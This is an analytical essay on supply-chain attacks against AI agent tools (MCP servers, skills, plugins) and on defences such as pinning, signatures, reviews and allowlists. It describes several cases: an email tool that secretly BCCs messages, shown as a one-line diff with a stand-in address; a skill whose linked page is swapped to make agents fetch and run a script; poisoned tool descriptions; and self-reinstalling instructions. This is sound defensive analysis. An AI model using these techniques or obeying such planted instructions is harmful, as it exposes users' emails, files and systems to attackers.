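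Koi says its monitoring software flagged the release as soon as the package's behaviour changed, and its researchers then read the code. The OSV record dates from 26 September, nine days after the release. Even if Koi's software flagged it immediately, people who relied on the public record had no warning for those nine days, and a seven-day cooldown would have ended two days before the record appeared.

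Koi also describes the package as a tool developers relied on every day before its author betrayed them. The dates don't fit this account very well, because they leave only two days for all 15 clean versions.

Koi reports 1,500 downloads a week, while The Hacker News reports 1,643 in total. Both can be right if the package was online for little more than a week. Koi guesses that a fifth of the weekly downloads were in active use, each by a different organisation, and that each organisation sent 10 to 50 emails a day. That gives 300 organisations and 3,000 to 15,000 copied emails a day. But the number of downloads isn't the number of users, and Koi, which sells a product for blocking such updates, offers no evidence for the one-fifth figure.

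Postmark confirmed that it had nothing to do with the postmark-mcp package and that somebody had used its name to steal email. A reviewer who checked the publisher could have rejected the package as an impostor on the first day. Checking the developer's reputation would have been less useful, since the developer, phanpak, maintained 31 other packages and, according to Koi, used a real name and had a GitHub profile full of legitimate projects. If Postmark's own developers had added the malicious line to the official server, checking the publisher wouldn't have helped.

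### Instructions on a page that can change

A tool's behaviour can also change without a new version. In June 2026 the security company AIR described an experiment with a skill called brand-landingpage, which interviews the user about a brand and designs a web page for it with Google's Stitch tool. Hoppe (2026), in *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, found no malicious line in the skill's main file. The file tells the agent to read Stitch's documentation at a link, treat that page as authoritative, install the software if it is missing, and not bother the user with the details. An honest author might write the same instructions for any new software, but the link led to a domain that AIR owned, with Stitch's name in it.

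The Hacker News (2026) describes what AIR did next:

1. AIR had the link lead to Google's real documentation. The scanners it tried, which included Cisco's, NVIDIA's and those on skills.sh, all passed the skill.
2. It submitted the skill to a GitHub collection of 156 skills with about 36,000 stars. The maintainers accepted it after a few days, and the skill then appeared to have those stars itself.
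3. It advertised the skill on Instagram to marketers, salespeople and designers.
4. Once enough people had installed the skill, AIR replaced the documentation with a page that told agents to download and run a script.

The script sent only the user's email address to AIR. An attacker's script could have read any files or reached any internal systems that the agent could access.

AIR says it reached about 26,000 agents this way, some of them on corporate accounts. Nobody else has confirmed the number, and AIR's write-up promotes a marketplace of vetted skills that the company was about to launch.

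There is much stronger evidence for the method than for the number. The scanners examined only the files in the package, and the ClawHavoc attackers had already kept their commands on a text-sharing site where they could replace them. Three weeks before AIR's report, the security company Trail of Bits had got past ClawHub's detector, Cisco's scanner and all three scanners on skills.sh. It pointed out that a scanner checks a fixed package, while an attacker can keep adjusting an attack until it passes. Hoppe found AIR's skill still in the GitHub collection on 23 September, three months after AIR publicly explained what it was.

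A reviewer could have caught this skill by checking who owned the linked domain. But even a link to Google's own site would have made the approval depend on a page that Google can edit. A company can copy the documentation into the skill and have the agent read the copy, which a reviewer can approve with the rest of the skill, but somebody then has to keep the copy up to date. Refusing every skill that links to outside instructions would be simpler, but it would exclude a lot of legitimate ones, because linking to documentation is normal.

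### When somebody else takes over the source

Many catalogues store only a link to a skill's GitHub repository, not a copy of the skill. When a developer renames a GitHub account, GitHub redirects the old link to the new name. But somebody else may be able to register the old account name and create a repository with the same name as the original, and anyone who follows the old link then gets that person's files. GitHub prevents this for repositories that have passed a certain number of downloads by retiring their names.

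Holzbauer and colleagues tested how many skills were vulnerable to this. They registered abandoned account names and checked whether GitHub would let them reuse the old repository names, without creating the repositories. Seven repositories were vulnerable, and 121 skills on skills.sh and SkillsDirectory, another catalogue, pointed to them. The vulnerable skills on skills.sh had a median of 25 downloads and a maximum of 2,032. The team tried only repositories with at least five stars, so the full number was probably higher. The team has kept the account names so that nobody else can use them. ClawHub avoids the problem because it distributes skills from its own copies.

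AIR gives much larger figures in *Plugin4Shell*, saying that 925 skills already in use were hijacked through the repositories behind them, affecting 134,000 agents. That is about 145 agents per skill, which is not implausible given that one skill had 2,032 downloads. The number of skills may also have grown since Holzbauer and colleagues collected their data in early 2026. But both figures come from AIR alone. The independent evidence indicates that the weakness exists, but on a smaller scale.

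Domains can change hands in a similar way. OX Security, which sells security software, surveyed 15,465 publicly listed MCP servers and described the results in The Hacker News' *Welcome to the Jungle* (2026). The servers used 5,095 hostnames, of which 2.3%, or about 117, no longer led to any machine. Six were on expired domains that anyone could register for $4 to $12 a year. The buyer would receive requests from every agent still configured to use the old server, and an allowlist entry for its address would still match. The buyer would also pass the MCP Registry's check of domain ownership, because they would own the domain.

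Six hostnames out of 5,095 is about one in 850, and probably few agents still call them, because a server on an expired domain doesn't work and most users would have stopped trying. OX conducted the survey itself, and accounts differ on how many registries it covered. OX's article says five, whereas Muncaster (2026), in *MCP Is Creating Major Governance Gaps, Researchers Warn*, lists three.

### Which remedies work against which changes

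Defenders have five main remedies. They can pin an approval to one version, require the publisher's signature, store a hash of the tool's descriptions, review every new version, or block a tool in an emergency. None of them works well against every kind of change:

| Remedy | Author releases a harmful version | Linked page changes | New owner takes over the repository | Remote operator changes the code |
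|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pin, checked against the files | Old version keeps running | No help | New code can't run | No files to check |
| Publisher's signature | No help, because the author signs it | No help | New code can't run, unless the new owner has the key | No help |
| Stored hash of descriptions | Helps only if the descriptions change | No help | Helps only if the descriptions change | Helps only if the descriptions change |
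| Review of each version | Helps if the reviewer notices | No help, unless somebody also watches the page | Helps if the reviewer notices | Reviewer can't see the code |
| Emergency block | Helps after discovery | Helps after discovery | Helps after discovery | Helps after discovery |

Pinning would have been enough against postmark-mcp. A company that had reviewed version 1.0.15 and approved a launch command ending in `postmark-mcp@1.0.15` would have stayed on the clean version, while one that had approved `postmark-mcp@latest` would have moved to 1.0.16. Pinning also works against a repository takeover if the pin includes a hash of the code, because any code the new owner changes would no longer match the hash.

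A marketplace can pin skills for all its users by keeping a fixed copy of each one, as Holzbauer and colleagues recommend. But a pin covers only the files it lists. Even with the strictest possible pin, AIR's skill would still have sent agents to the replaced page. In SafeDep's demonstration, a package that the skill's script downloaded changed, while the skill did not.

### Four agents that didn't check their pins

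Pinning a tool to a version works only if the agent confirms that it received that version. In May 2026, AIR found that the coding agents Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex, GitHub Copilot and Google's Gemini CLI failed to do this. It published the flaw in September under the name Plugin4Shell.

A plugin marketplace can pin a plugin to a commit, which is one exact state of the code in a repository. Git, which stores the code, identifies each commit by a 40-character hash. The agents requested the pinned commit from Git but never checked that the code they received matched it. Git can also look up code by labels that the repository's owner chooses, and AIR found that the owner could use such a label to make the request return different code. The agent would install that code and report that it had respected the pin. According to AIR, this could happen to somebody who already had the plugin without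 them clicking on anything.

An attacker first needed control of the plugin's repository, either as its author or by taking it over. Pins are meant to guard against this. In *Plugin4Shell*, Constantin (2026) describes the fix as one line of code that compares the installed version with the pin and stops if they differ.

Digital Matters' *Plugin4Shell* (2026) compared AIR's account with the vendors' own pages on 27 September:

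| Agent | Status |
|---|---|
| Claude Code | Fixed in version 2.1.179, released on 16 June |
| Codex | Fixed in version 0.146.0 |
| GitHub Copilot | No fix found |
| Gemini CLI | Google won't fix it and is retiring the program for most users |

OpenAI's changelog includes the new check, so AIR isn't the only source for the Codex fix. Anthropic's release notes don't mention one, and the version number for Claude Code comes from AIR, which says Anthropic confirmed it. GitHub's documentation still described a pinned plugin as safe from this kind of change.

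AIR claims in its headline that the flaw affected "millions of agents". That figure can only mean agents that had the flaw, not agents that were attacked. AIR concedes that a marketplace could block the trick in three of the four products by accepting only plugins hosted on GitHub, because GitHub refuses the kind of label the trick needs. If so, plugins hosted there were apparently safe from it in every agent but Gemini CLI. Holzbauer and colleagues found that GitHub hosts most skills, and if the same is true of plugins, the practical danger was much smaller than the headline suggests. AIR also says that customers of its own marketplace were not affected, a claim that promotes that marketplace.

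The flaw is still a good reason to test pins before relying on them. An administrator can pin a harmless test plugin, change its code and see what the agent installs. This test wouldn't have revealed the trick described here, but it would expose an agent that ignores pins altogether.

### Signatures and stored descriptions

A publisher signs a tool with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check that the signature is genuine and the tool hasn't changed since. Signing helps when a repository or domain changes hands, because the new owner normally won't have the old key. It doesn't protect against a dishonest author. The developer of postmark-mcp could have signed version 1.0.16 with the same key as the 15 versions before it.

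MCP itself requires none of this. Shen and colleagues note that the protocol requires no protection for the integrity of a server's content, and they recommend signing tool descriptions and identifying packages by a hash of their contents.

The best-known proposal for adding such protection is the Enhanced Tool Definition Interface, which *ETDI* (2025) sets out. It works roughly like this:

1. The provider writes a definition of each tool, with its name, description, input and output formats, version number and required permissions, and signs it.
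2. Before showing the tool to the user or the model, the agent's application checks the signature against the provider's public key. If the check fails, it can hide the tool, warn the user or block it.
3. The user approves that version of the definition.
4. If the tool changes, the provider has to issue a new version with a new signature, and the application asks the user again.

*Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, describes a central registry that would keep public keys, signed tool definitions and a log of changes, so anyone could audit a tool's history.

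An application can get part of this benefit without the provider's help. It hashes each tool's name, description and input format at approval, then recomputes and compares the hash at every later connection. Suppose a weather tool's description read "Returns the forecast for a city" when the user approved it, and a month later the server adds a sentence telling the agent to include the user's private notes in each request. The hash no longer matches, so the application can withhold the new description from the model until someone has reviewed it. This is an effective defence against attacks through descriptions, and it takes little computation. It also works for remote servers, because they have to send their descriptions to the agent.

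It would have missed postmark-mcp, though, because the extra line was in the server's code and the agent saw the same email tool as before. ETDI does a little better, since it also requires a new version when the code changes. But the application can't see the code, so it depends on the provider to declare the change, and a provider who is stealing email has no reason to. Even if phanpak had declared version 1.0.16, users would have been asked to approve a tool whose description looked the same. Nearly all of them would have said yes, judging by how rarely Anthropic's testers refused even a clearly dangerous command.

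An approval can also be too broad even when the tool hasn't changed. Muncaster reports a test by OX in which a malicious server asked Claude Code for a harmless file and the user chose "always allow". The server then asked for the kind of file that holds passwords and got it without another prompt. According to OX, Anthropic replied that the setting works as documented. OX used Haiku 3.5, an old and small model, and a newer one might have been better at spotting the malicious request. But Anthropic doesn't regard that ability as a security boundary, so a better result with a newer model wouldn't show that the approval is safe.

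### Reviewing what changed

A person who compares two versions of a tool has a much easier job than one who reviews it from scratch. In simplified form, a comparison of postmark-mcp 1.0.15 with 1.0.16 would have looked something like this:

```diff
   to: message.to,
+  bcc: "developer@example.net",
   subject: message.subject,
```

The plus sign marks the new line. A reviewer who knew what BCC means would probably have questioned it here, but the same line is easy to overlook in a file of several hundred lines. Koi's software seems to have worked in a similar way, since a change in behaviour triggered it.

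A tool has to be reviewed again whenever its code changes. Microsoft re-reviews a server when its description changes, so the BCC line would have gone through because it changed only the code. Cursor reviews every plugin update by hand, which would have given a reviewer the chance to see the line.

Such reviews take a lot of time because tools change so often. If a company has approved 40 tools and each releases a new version every two weeks, it has 1,040 comparisons to make a year, which take 260 hours at 15 minutes each. Reading all 40 tools once, at half an hour each, takes only 20 hours. The company could instead update each tool once a quarter, for 160 comparisons and about 40 hours, although each comparison would cover more changes and probably take longer. Its agents would also run older versions between updates.

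### Why a remote server can't be pinned

A pin works by checking a tool's files against a recorded hash. An agent that uses a remote server receives only tool descriptions and answers, so there are no files to check. The application can record the server's address, its certificate and a hash of the descriptions, but the operator can replace all the server's code without changing any of these.

Publishing the source code doesn't solve this because, as OX points out, a remote server can run entirely different code from what its public repository contains. A reviewer who reads the repository has to trust that the server runs the same code. OX also found that 15.6% of the hostnames led to machines outside the United States. An operator could start on an American machine and later send traffic abroad, and a company that approved the server because of where it kept data might never find out.

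Regular testing helps a little. The company can send the server the same requests every week and check whether the answers change. But a remote email server that started keeping copies of emails would still give the same answers, and an operator who recognised the tester could behave well only for them, just as phishing sites show harmless pages to security companies' crawlers.

If the source code is available, the company can run the server on its own machines and can review and pin the server's files. That suits a tool that converts documents but not one that connects to somebody else's service. For an accounting service, the sensible choice is the server that the accounting provider operates. That server could still change without notice, but the provider already holds the company's invoices, so using its server exposes them to nobody new. An unknown third party's server for the same service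 is a much worse choice, because approving it means trusting another operator indefinitely.

A company that still has to use such a server can limit what the server receives. If the company gives it a login that can read invoices but not make payments, the operator can't change those permissions by changing the server's code. The recipient rule described earlier for Amazon's mail service would also still work, as long as the remote server sends its messages through the company's own account.

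### Stopping a tool that has already changed

When someone discovers a bad change, the first task is to stop the copies already in use. After Koi contacted the developer of postmark-mcp, the developer deleted the package from npm. That prevented new installations from npm, but Koi points out that every installed copy of the bad version kept copying emails.

An emergency block therefore has to reach the agent. A denylist that overrides the allowlist, as in Claude Code, can stop a server from loading on every machine the company manages. Deleting the tool's files may not be enough. The Next Web's *Malicious AI ‘skills’ turned agents into credential thieves, at scale* describes a skill that told the agent to rewrite its own standing instructions so that it would reinstall the skill if it was deleted. Blocking the skill from loading would still stop the reinstalled copy if the block matched something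 the copy kept, such as its name or files.

Staff also have to deal with any data the tool has already taken. For postmark-mcp, Koi advised users to change any passwords or keys they had sent by email and to search their mail logs for copies sent to the developer's domain. For a skill like AIR's, blocking the linked domain would stop agents from reading the page, even on machines where the skill was still installed.

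### Security fixes that a pin keeps out

Pinning a tool to one version blocks good changes as well as bad ones. According to Shen and colleagues, the command-running flaw in mcp-remote affected hundreds of thousands of developers' environments. Anyone who had pinned a vulnerable version kept the flaw until they changed the pin, no matter how quickly mcp-remote's own developers fixed it.

The delay depends on how often the company updates. If fixes come out at random times, a company that updates quarterly waits an average of about 45 days for one, and a company that updates monthly waits about 15. As with a cooldown, attackers can exploit the flaw in the meantime. Missing fixes could well do more harm than the attacks that pinning prevents, since insecure tools seem to be much more common than hostile ones. But comparing their numbers isn't enough to tell which risk is greater, because a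 flaw does harm only if somebody exploits it, while a hostile tool is made to do harm.

A company can reduce the delay by pinning its tools and subscribing to security advisories, so that a published warning triggers an immediate review. This works only if the developers announce the fix. Anthropic's nine release notes for Claude Code 2.1.179 covered changes such as those to dropped connections and scrolling, but not the check on pinned plugins. An administrator who read them would have had no reason to update quickly. When AIR published the flaw three months later, anyone still on an older version was running an agent with a publicly known weakness. By 18 September none of the four vendors had issued an advisory, and the flaw had no number in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities that many companies use to decide what to patch.

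Pinning an unmaintained tool to one version has almost no downside, because there are no fixes to miss. The NSA says many popular MCP servers are unmaintained. But any flaws in such a tool will stay unfixed, and someone could take it over through an abandoned account or an expired domain. A company that still wants the tool is probably better off keeping and repairing its own copy.

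## What it costs to refuse unknown tools

Reviewing tools, and reviewing them again whenever they change, takes a lot of staff time, and nearly all of it goes on tools that turn out to be harmless. Meanwhile the people who asked for those tools have to work without them. This is the main objection to allowlists. Critics add that people who wait too long will find another way to get a tool, and that whoever keeps the list gains power over everyone who wants to be on it.

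### What a short list leaves out

No one could review a whole public catalogue by hand. SkillsMP alone indexes more than four million skill files, although many are probably duplicates. Quasa's *Agent Skills Reached 3.8 Million Files* (2026) describes GitSkills, a dataset of 3,797,117 skill files that researchers collected from public GitHub repositories in July 2026. Just over half were exact copies, which left 1,877,981 different texts. Reading them all once, at half an hour each, would take about 940,000 hours. Vercel counted a million new skills in seven months (*Vercel counts a million skills in seven months*, 2026), and reading those as they arrived, at the same pace, would take more than 400 people working full time.

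But most people use only a tiny fraction of the available tools. In early December 2026, AgentMarketIndex's *MCP servers ranked by measured installs* listed 78,140 servers, nearly all from the official MCP Registry, and had download counts for 24,806 of them. The top 200 accounted for 84.9% of the 99 million downloads over 30 days, and the top ten for about 65%. At two hours each, one person could review those 200 servers in ten weeks.

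Downloads only roughly measure use, and the counts leave out the other 53,334 servers, including any that run remotely and have no package to download. Still, downloads are so concentrated that a fairly short allowlist could probably cover most of what people do with MCP servers.

Such a list burdens people with unusual needs. The remaining 15% of downloads are spread over about 24,600 servers, averaging about 600 a month each. People who are refused the only server for an obscure database have no substitute, whereas those refused one of several calendar servers can use another.

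### A hypothetical review queue

Suppose a company's employees request 20 new tools a month and a full review takes two hours, which is not much time for the work involved. Under the checklist in Anthropic's *Skills for enterprise*, the reviewer lists every command, file operation and tool that a skill uses, checks where its links lead, and looks for instructions that would send sensitive data out.

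To keep the example simple, the company approves everything it reviews. Each approved tool releases two new versions a month, and each version takes 15 minutes to compare with the previous one. The reviewers have 60 hours a month in total. They review updates first, because people already depend on those tools. All of these figures are invented.

| Month | Hours spent on updates | New tools reviewed | Requests waiting at the end |
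|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0 | 20 | 0 |
| 3 | 20 | 20 | 0 |
| 4 | 30 | 15 | 5 |
| 6 | 43 | 8 | 25 |
| 9 | 53 | 4 | 71 |
| 12 | 57 | 1 or 2 | about 125 |

Reviewing updates to each approved tool takes half an hour a month for as long as the tool stays on the list. With 60 hours a month, the list can't grow past 120 tools, because updates would then take up all the reviewers' time. Doubling the hours would only raise the limit to 240. The company could easily think it has enough reviewers, because they keep up for three months.

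The company can do better by reducing the work that each tool creates:

| Change | First month with a backlog | Requests waiting after a year |
|---|---|---|
| None | 4 | about 125 |
| An outside reviewer handles half the tools and their updates | 9 | about 16 |
| A scanner checks updates, and people read only those it flags (6.3% of them) | 33 | 0 |
| The same, but the scanner flags 36.6% | 7 | about 29 |
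| People compare versions once a quarter | 14 | 0 |

The second row uses an assumed time of 15 minutes to accept an outside review. SafeDep's *The State of MCP Registries* argues that the official registry needs a vetted, security-first catalogue built on top of it, which could supply such reviews. SafeDep sells security software, but the arithmetic supports its argument. If a thousand companies want the same 200 servers, it is wasteful for each to read the same code. Each company would still have to decide whether a tool suits its own work, and a mistake in a shared review would affect all of them.

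The two scanner rows use false-positive rates from the tests of whole skills described earlier, and the rates for updates could be quite different. The company would also run any harmful update the scanner missed, so it might reasonably let the scanner clear updates to a tool that formats text but have a person read every update to one that sends email.

### When people stop waiting

By the end of the first year in the example, about 125 requests are waiting and the reviewers finish one or two a month. Hardly any employees will wait that long. They can instead install the tool on a personal laptop and send work files there, or use an agent that the company doesn't manage.

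Suppose 40 of them do. The company now has about 115 reviewed tools and 40 that nobody there has reviewed. If malicious tools are as common among those 40 as in the catalogues that Liu and colleagues searched, there is about a 6% chance that at least one is malicious. The company also can't find or block these tools when one is reported to be malicious. Its denylist doesn't apply to personal laptops, and a search of its records for postmark-mcp would find nothing even if several employees were using it.

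A very strict allowlist can leave a company knowing less about the tools its staff use than a looser one that logs everything, because some people will go around the strict one. They are more likely to do so the more they need a tool and the longer they have to wait for approval. A company can give them a better option by letting them try unreviewed tools immediately in a sandbox. This won't help someone whose work requires confidential files, but it lets people find out whether a tool is worth two hours of a reviewer's time.

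### Servers that agents install from memory

Sometimes the agent picks an unreviewed tool, and the user may not notice. Zorz (2026), in *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched*, reports on research into this pattern by Glow Labs, part of a security company. Glow Labs, which calls the pattern MCPhantom, read transcripts of real coding sessions in which an agent had installed or suggested an abandoned MCP server. In 98% of these sessions, the agent appears to have taken the server's name from the model's training data. In the other 2%, the user had asked for the old package by name.

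In one case, a developer wanted a GitHub server. GitHub maintains its own, but the agent chose an old one that Anthropic had published as a reference example. The old server's repository has a notice that the server will get no more security updates. Glow Labs saw the same behaviour in Claude Code, Cursor and OpenAI's Codex, among others, with models from three companies.

The 98% figure doesn't measure how often agents do this, because Glow Labs looked only at sessions where an abandoned server came up. Zorz also reports more than 17.3 million npm downloads of the abandoned packages since July 2025. These downloads show that many machines still run this code, but they don't measure the agents' mistakes either, because some must come from old configurations that start the same server every day.

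Glow Labs found four serious flaws in the abandoned servers. The worst is in a server that lets an agent control a web browser through a program called Puppeteer. Hidden instructions on a web page can get the agent to start any program on the machine instead of the browser. The developer approved web browsing, but the agent's application applies that approval to whatever the server starts. The maintainers replied that they had archived the server in May 2025 and wouldn't fix it. Glow Labs has not seen anyone exploit the flaws.

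A blocklist of malware would not stop these servers, because their developers meant no harm. Security software on the machine doesn't flag them either, because Node.js routinely installs public packages. Programs that check a project's dependencies miss them because the agent never adds the server to the project's dependency list. The flaws also aren't listed in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities.

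An allowlist would block the abandoned packages unless someone had approved them. Five of them are among the hundred most downloaded MCP packages on npm, so a company that built its list from download counts could easily include them. Most users should lose little by refusing these servers, since GitHub's own server does the same job and still gets security updates.

The program that runs the agent has to enforce the list, because the model can't be relied on to do so. In one session, an agent looked up a package on npm, received a deprecation notice, and installed the package anyway without telling the user. A company that writes "use only approved servers" in the agent's instructions is relying on the same model to notice and follow them, and a malicious web page can give the model contrary instructions.

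If the application checks the list before it starts a server, the model's choice matters much less. If the agent proposes the abandoned package, the application finds no match, refuses to start it, and can show the agent the approved GitHub server instead. The check also has to cover the agent's shell, because an agent that is refused could try to start the same package with an ordinary command, just to finish the task.

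Nadav Claude Cohen, a researcher at Glow, wants the makers of coding agents to block abandoned servers by default, including those already installed. This would protect people who have no allowlist, but only if every maker did it. Cohen thinks retraining models to forget the old names is too expensive to be likely.

### Who gets the screening

Automatic screening could help small companies most, since they have nobody to read code, but Anthropic offers it to larger customers. According to Anthropic's *Get started with skill and plugin scanning*, it is available on Enterprise plans, where Claude scans each third-party skill or plugin when somebody uploads or edits it. The scan usually takes a minute or two, and Claude then passes the skill or plugin, attaches a warning or blocks it. An administrator can allow a blocked version, but Claude scans the next version too. This is close to the screening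 of updates in the example, except that nobody has to compare the versions that pass.

Novaknown's *Anthropic Sold Small Teams Claude Add-ons and Kept the Malware Check* (2026) objects that companies on the cheaper Team plan can use the same kinds of add-ons without the malware check. The Team plan is for 2 to 150 people, while Enterprise has a minimum of 20 seats, so a company of ten that wanted the check would have to buy twice as many seats as it needs. It would also pay separately for usage, because the Enterprise seat fee covers only access (Anthropic's *What is the Enterprise plan?*).

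Anthropic tells companies without the scanner to read a skill's files themselves. Novaknown points out that administrators on the Team plan can see the names of skills that employees create but not the files. Microsoft scans every extension in its VS Code marketplace for all users for free.

Novaknown's complaint is mostly fair, though it overlooks the automated screening of submissions to one of Anthropic's public plugin marketplaces, which protects anyone who installs from there. Computing costs seem a weak reason to withhold the scan. Scanning 20 skills a month for a small company would cost Anthropic $11 at 55 cents a skill, the highest price Yang and colleagues measured. NIST also considers allowlists generally infeasible for small offices, so many of the companies without the scan can't easily keep an allowlist either.

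Even on an Enterprise plan, the check leaves out MCP servers and any skills the organisation had before it turned scanning on. It also leaves out organisations that hold their own encryption keys, have Anthropic retain none of their data, or use Anthropic's settings for US health-privacy law, so some of the customers with the most sensitive data don't get it. Anthropic doesn't scan skills that developers upload through its API either, and advises those developers to use the manual checklist and pin versions.

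### Android and the power of a gatekeeper

Whoever decides which tools people may run can also use that power for other purposes. Google's new rules for Android apps have prompted this argument on a very large scale.

Frey (2025), in *A new layer of security for certified Android devices*, announced that Android would require a verified developer to register every app, including apps from outside Google's store. The rule applies to certified devices, which ship with Google's services. F-Droid, a non-profit store for free and open-source apps and one of the rule's main opponents, says these make up more than 95% of Android devices outside China (The Hacker News, *Google Sets Sept. 30 Deadline for Android Developer Verification in Four Countries*, 2026).

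Frey, a Google vice-president, compares the rule to an airport ID check, which is separate from the screening of bags. Google confirms who the developer is but doesn't review the app. This makes rotation harder, because after Google removes a malicious app, its author can't return the next day under a new name without finding another identity to register.

Google also says it found over 50 times more malware in apps downloaded from the internet than in those on Google Play. Frey doesn't explain how Google counted. In Kotzias and colleagues' figures from 2019, the gap is about six times for apps from websites, though those figures also include nuisances such as adware. Google Play reviews apps as well as checking identities, so neither gap shows how much identity checks alone would achieve.

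Android's developer verification rule took effect on 30 September 2026 in Brazil, Indonesia, Singapore and Thailand, but only for seven participating stores. *Android developer verification will reach every install source* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that Google will start extending it to all countries in January 2027 and, over several months, to every source of apps. Google says registered apps already make up more than 99% of Android installs. As with MCP servers, the small share that remains can include many little-used apps, and Pogorelec notes that it matters to the developers of those apps.

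Google has made two concessions to these developers and their users. Students and hobbyists can open an account without a fee or government ID and share their apps with up to 50 devices, a limit Google raised from 20. Users can also choose to install unregistered apps. According to *Android’s controversial sideloading rules go global in January* (Simons, 2026), they must first turn on a setting in the developer options, confirm that nobody is pressuring them, restart the phone and wait 24 hours. They can then allow unregistered apps for seven days or indefinitely. The wait is meant to stop scammers who talk victims through an installation over the phone, and it could well work, since such scams depend on rushing the victim.

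Independent developers still object to the rule. Keep Android Open, a campaign against it, says that malware authors can register while dissidents and small developers often can't. Its warning that Google will block every unregistered app with no way to opt out is wrong now that the 24-hour procedure exists. Its better argument is that this procedure runs through Google Play Services, which Google can change at any time without updating Android, so Google could withdraw the exception whenever it chose.

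F-Droid says the rule would end the project, because it can neither make its developers register with Google nor take over their apps' identifiers itself (Neowin, *Google's shocking developer decree struggles to justify the urgent threat to F-Droid*). In September 2026 it was still operating and preparing its biggest update in a decade (Mehta, 2026, *F-Droid's biggest update in a decade is coming despite Google's sideloading crackdown*). But the rule did not yet apply to stores like F-Droid, so its survival is little evidence of whether the fear was justified. Google has since published a guide to registering apps from open-source catalogues, but the guide doesn't help developers who refuse to give Google a name.

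More than 40 organisations signed an open letter against the rule, objecting that Google is extending its authority into channels where it has "no legitimate operational role" (TechRadar's *Proton, Tor, AdGuard among 40+ asking Google*). EFF, a digital rights group, notes that Google announced the rule while fighting a court order to stop punishing developers who use competing stores, and thinks registration could help Google keep its monopoly. Google may sincerely want less malware and still gain this advantage. The blind pseudonyms that Friedman and Resnick proposed would let a developer stay anonymous but wouldn't determine who gets to ban developers.

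No company has that much control over agent tools yet. Claude Code's users can add any marketplace unless their employer forbids it. But some software makers already exempt certain tools from their rules, as Copilot does with GitHub's own servers and VS Code does with some publishers' extensions. Both exemptions may have good security reasons, since the publishers are known. If the maker of a popular agent allowed only tools from its own list, though, it could refuse a competitor's tool and call the decision a security measure, and outsiders would struggle to tell whether that was true.

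An employer's allowlist gives its keeper much less power. If one company refuses a tool, the publisher can still offer it to every other company, and the employee who wanted it can ask the reviewer to reconsider.
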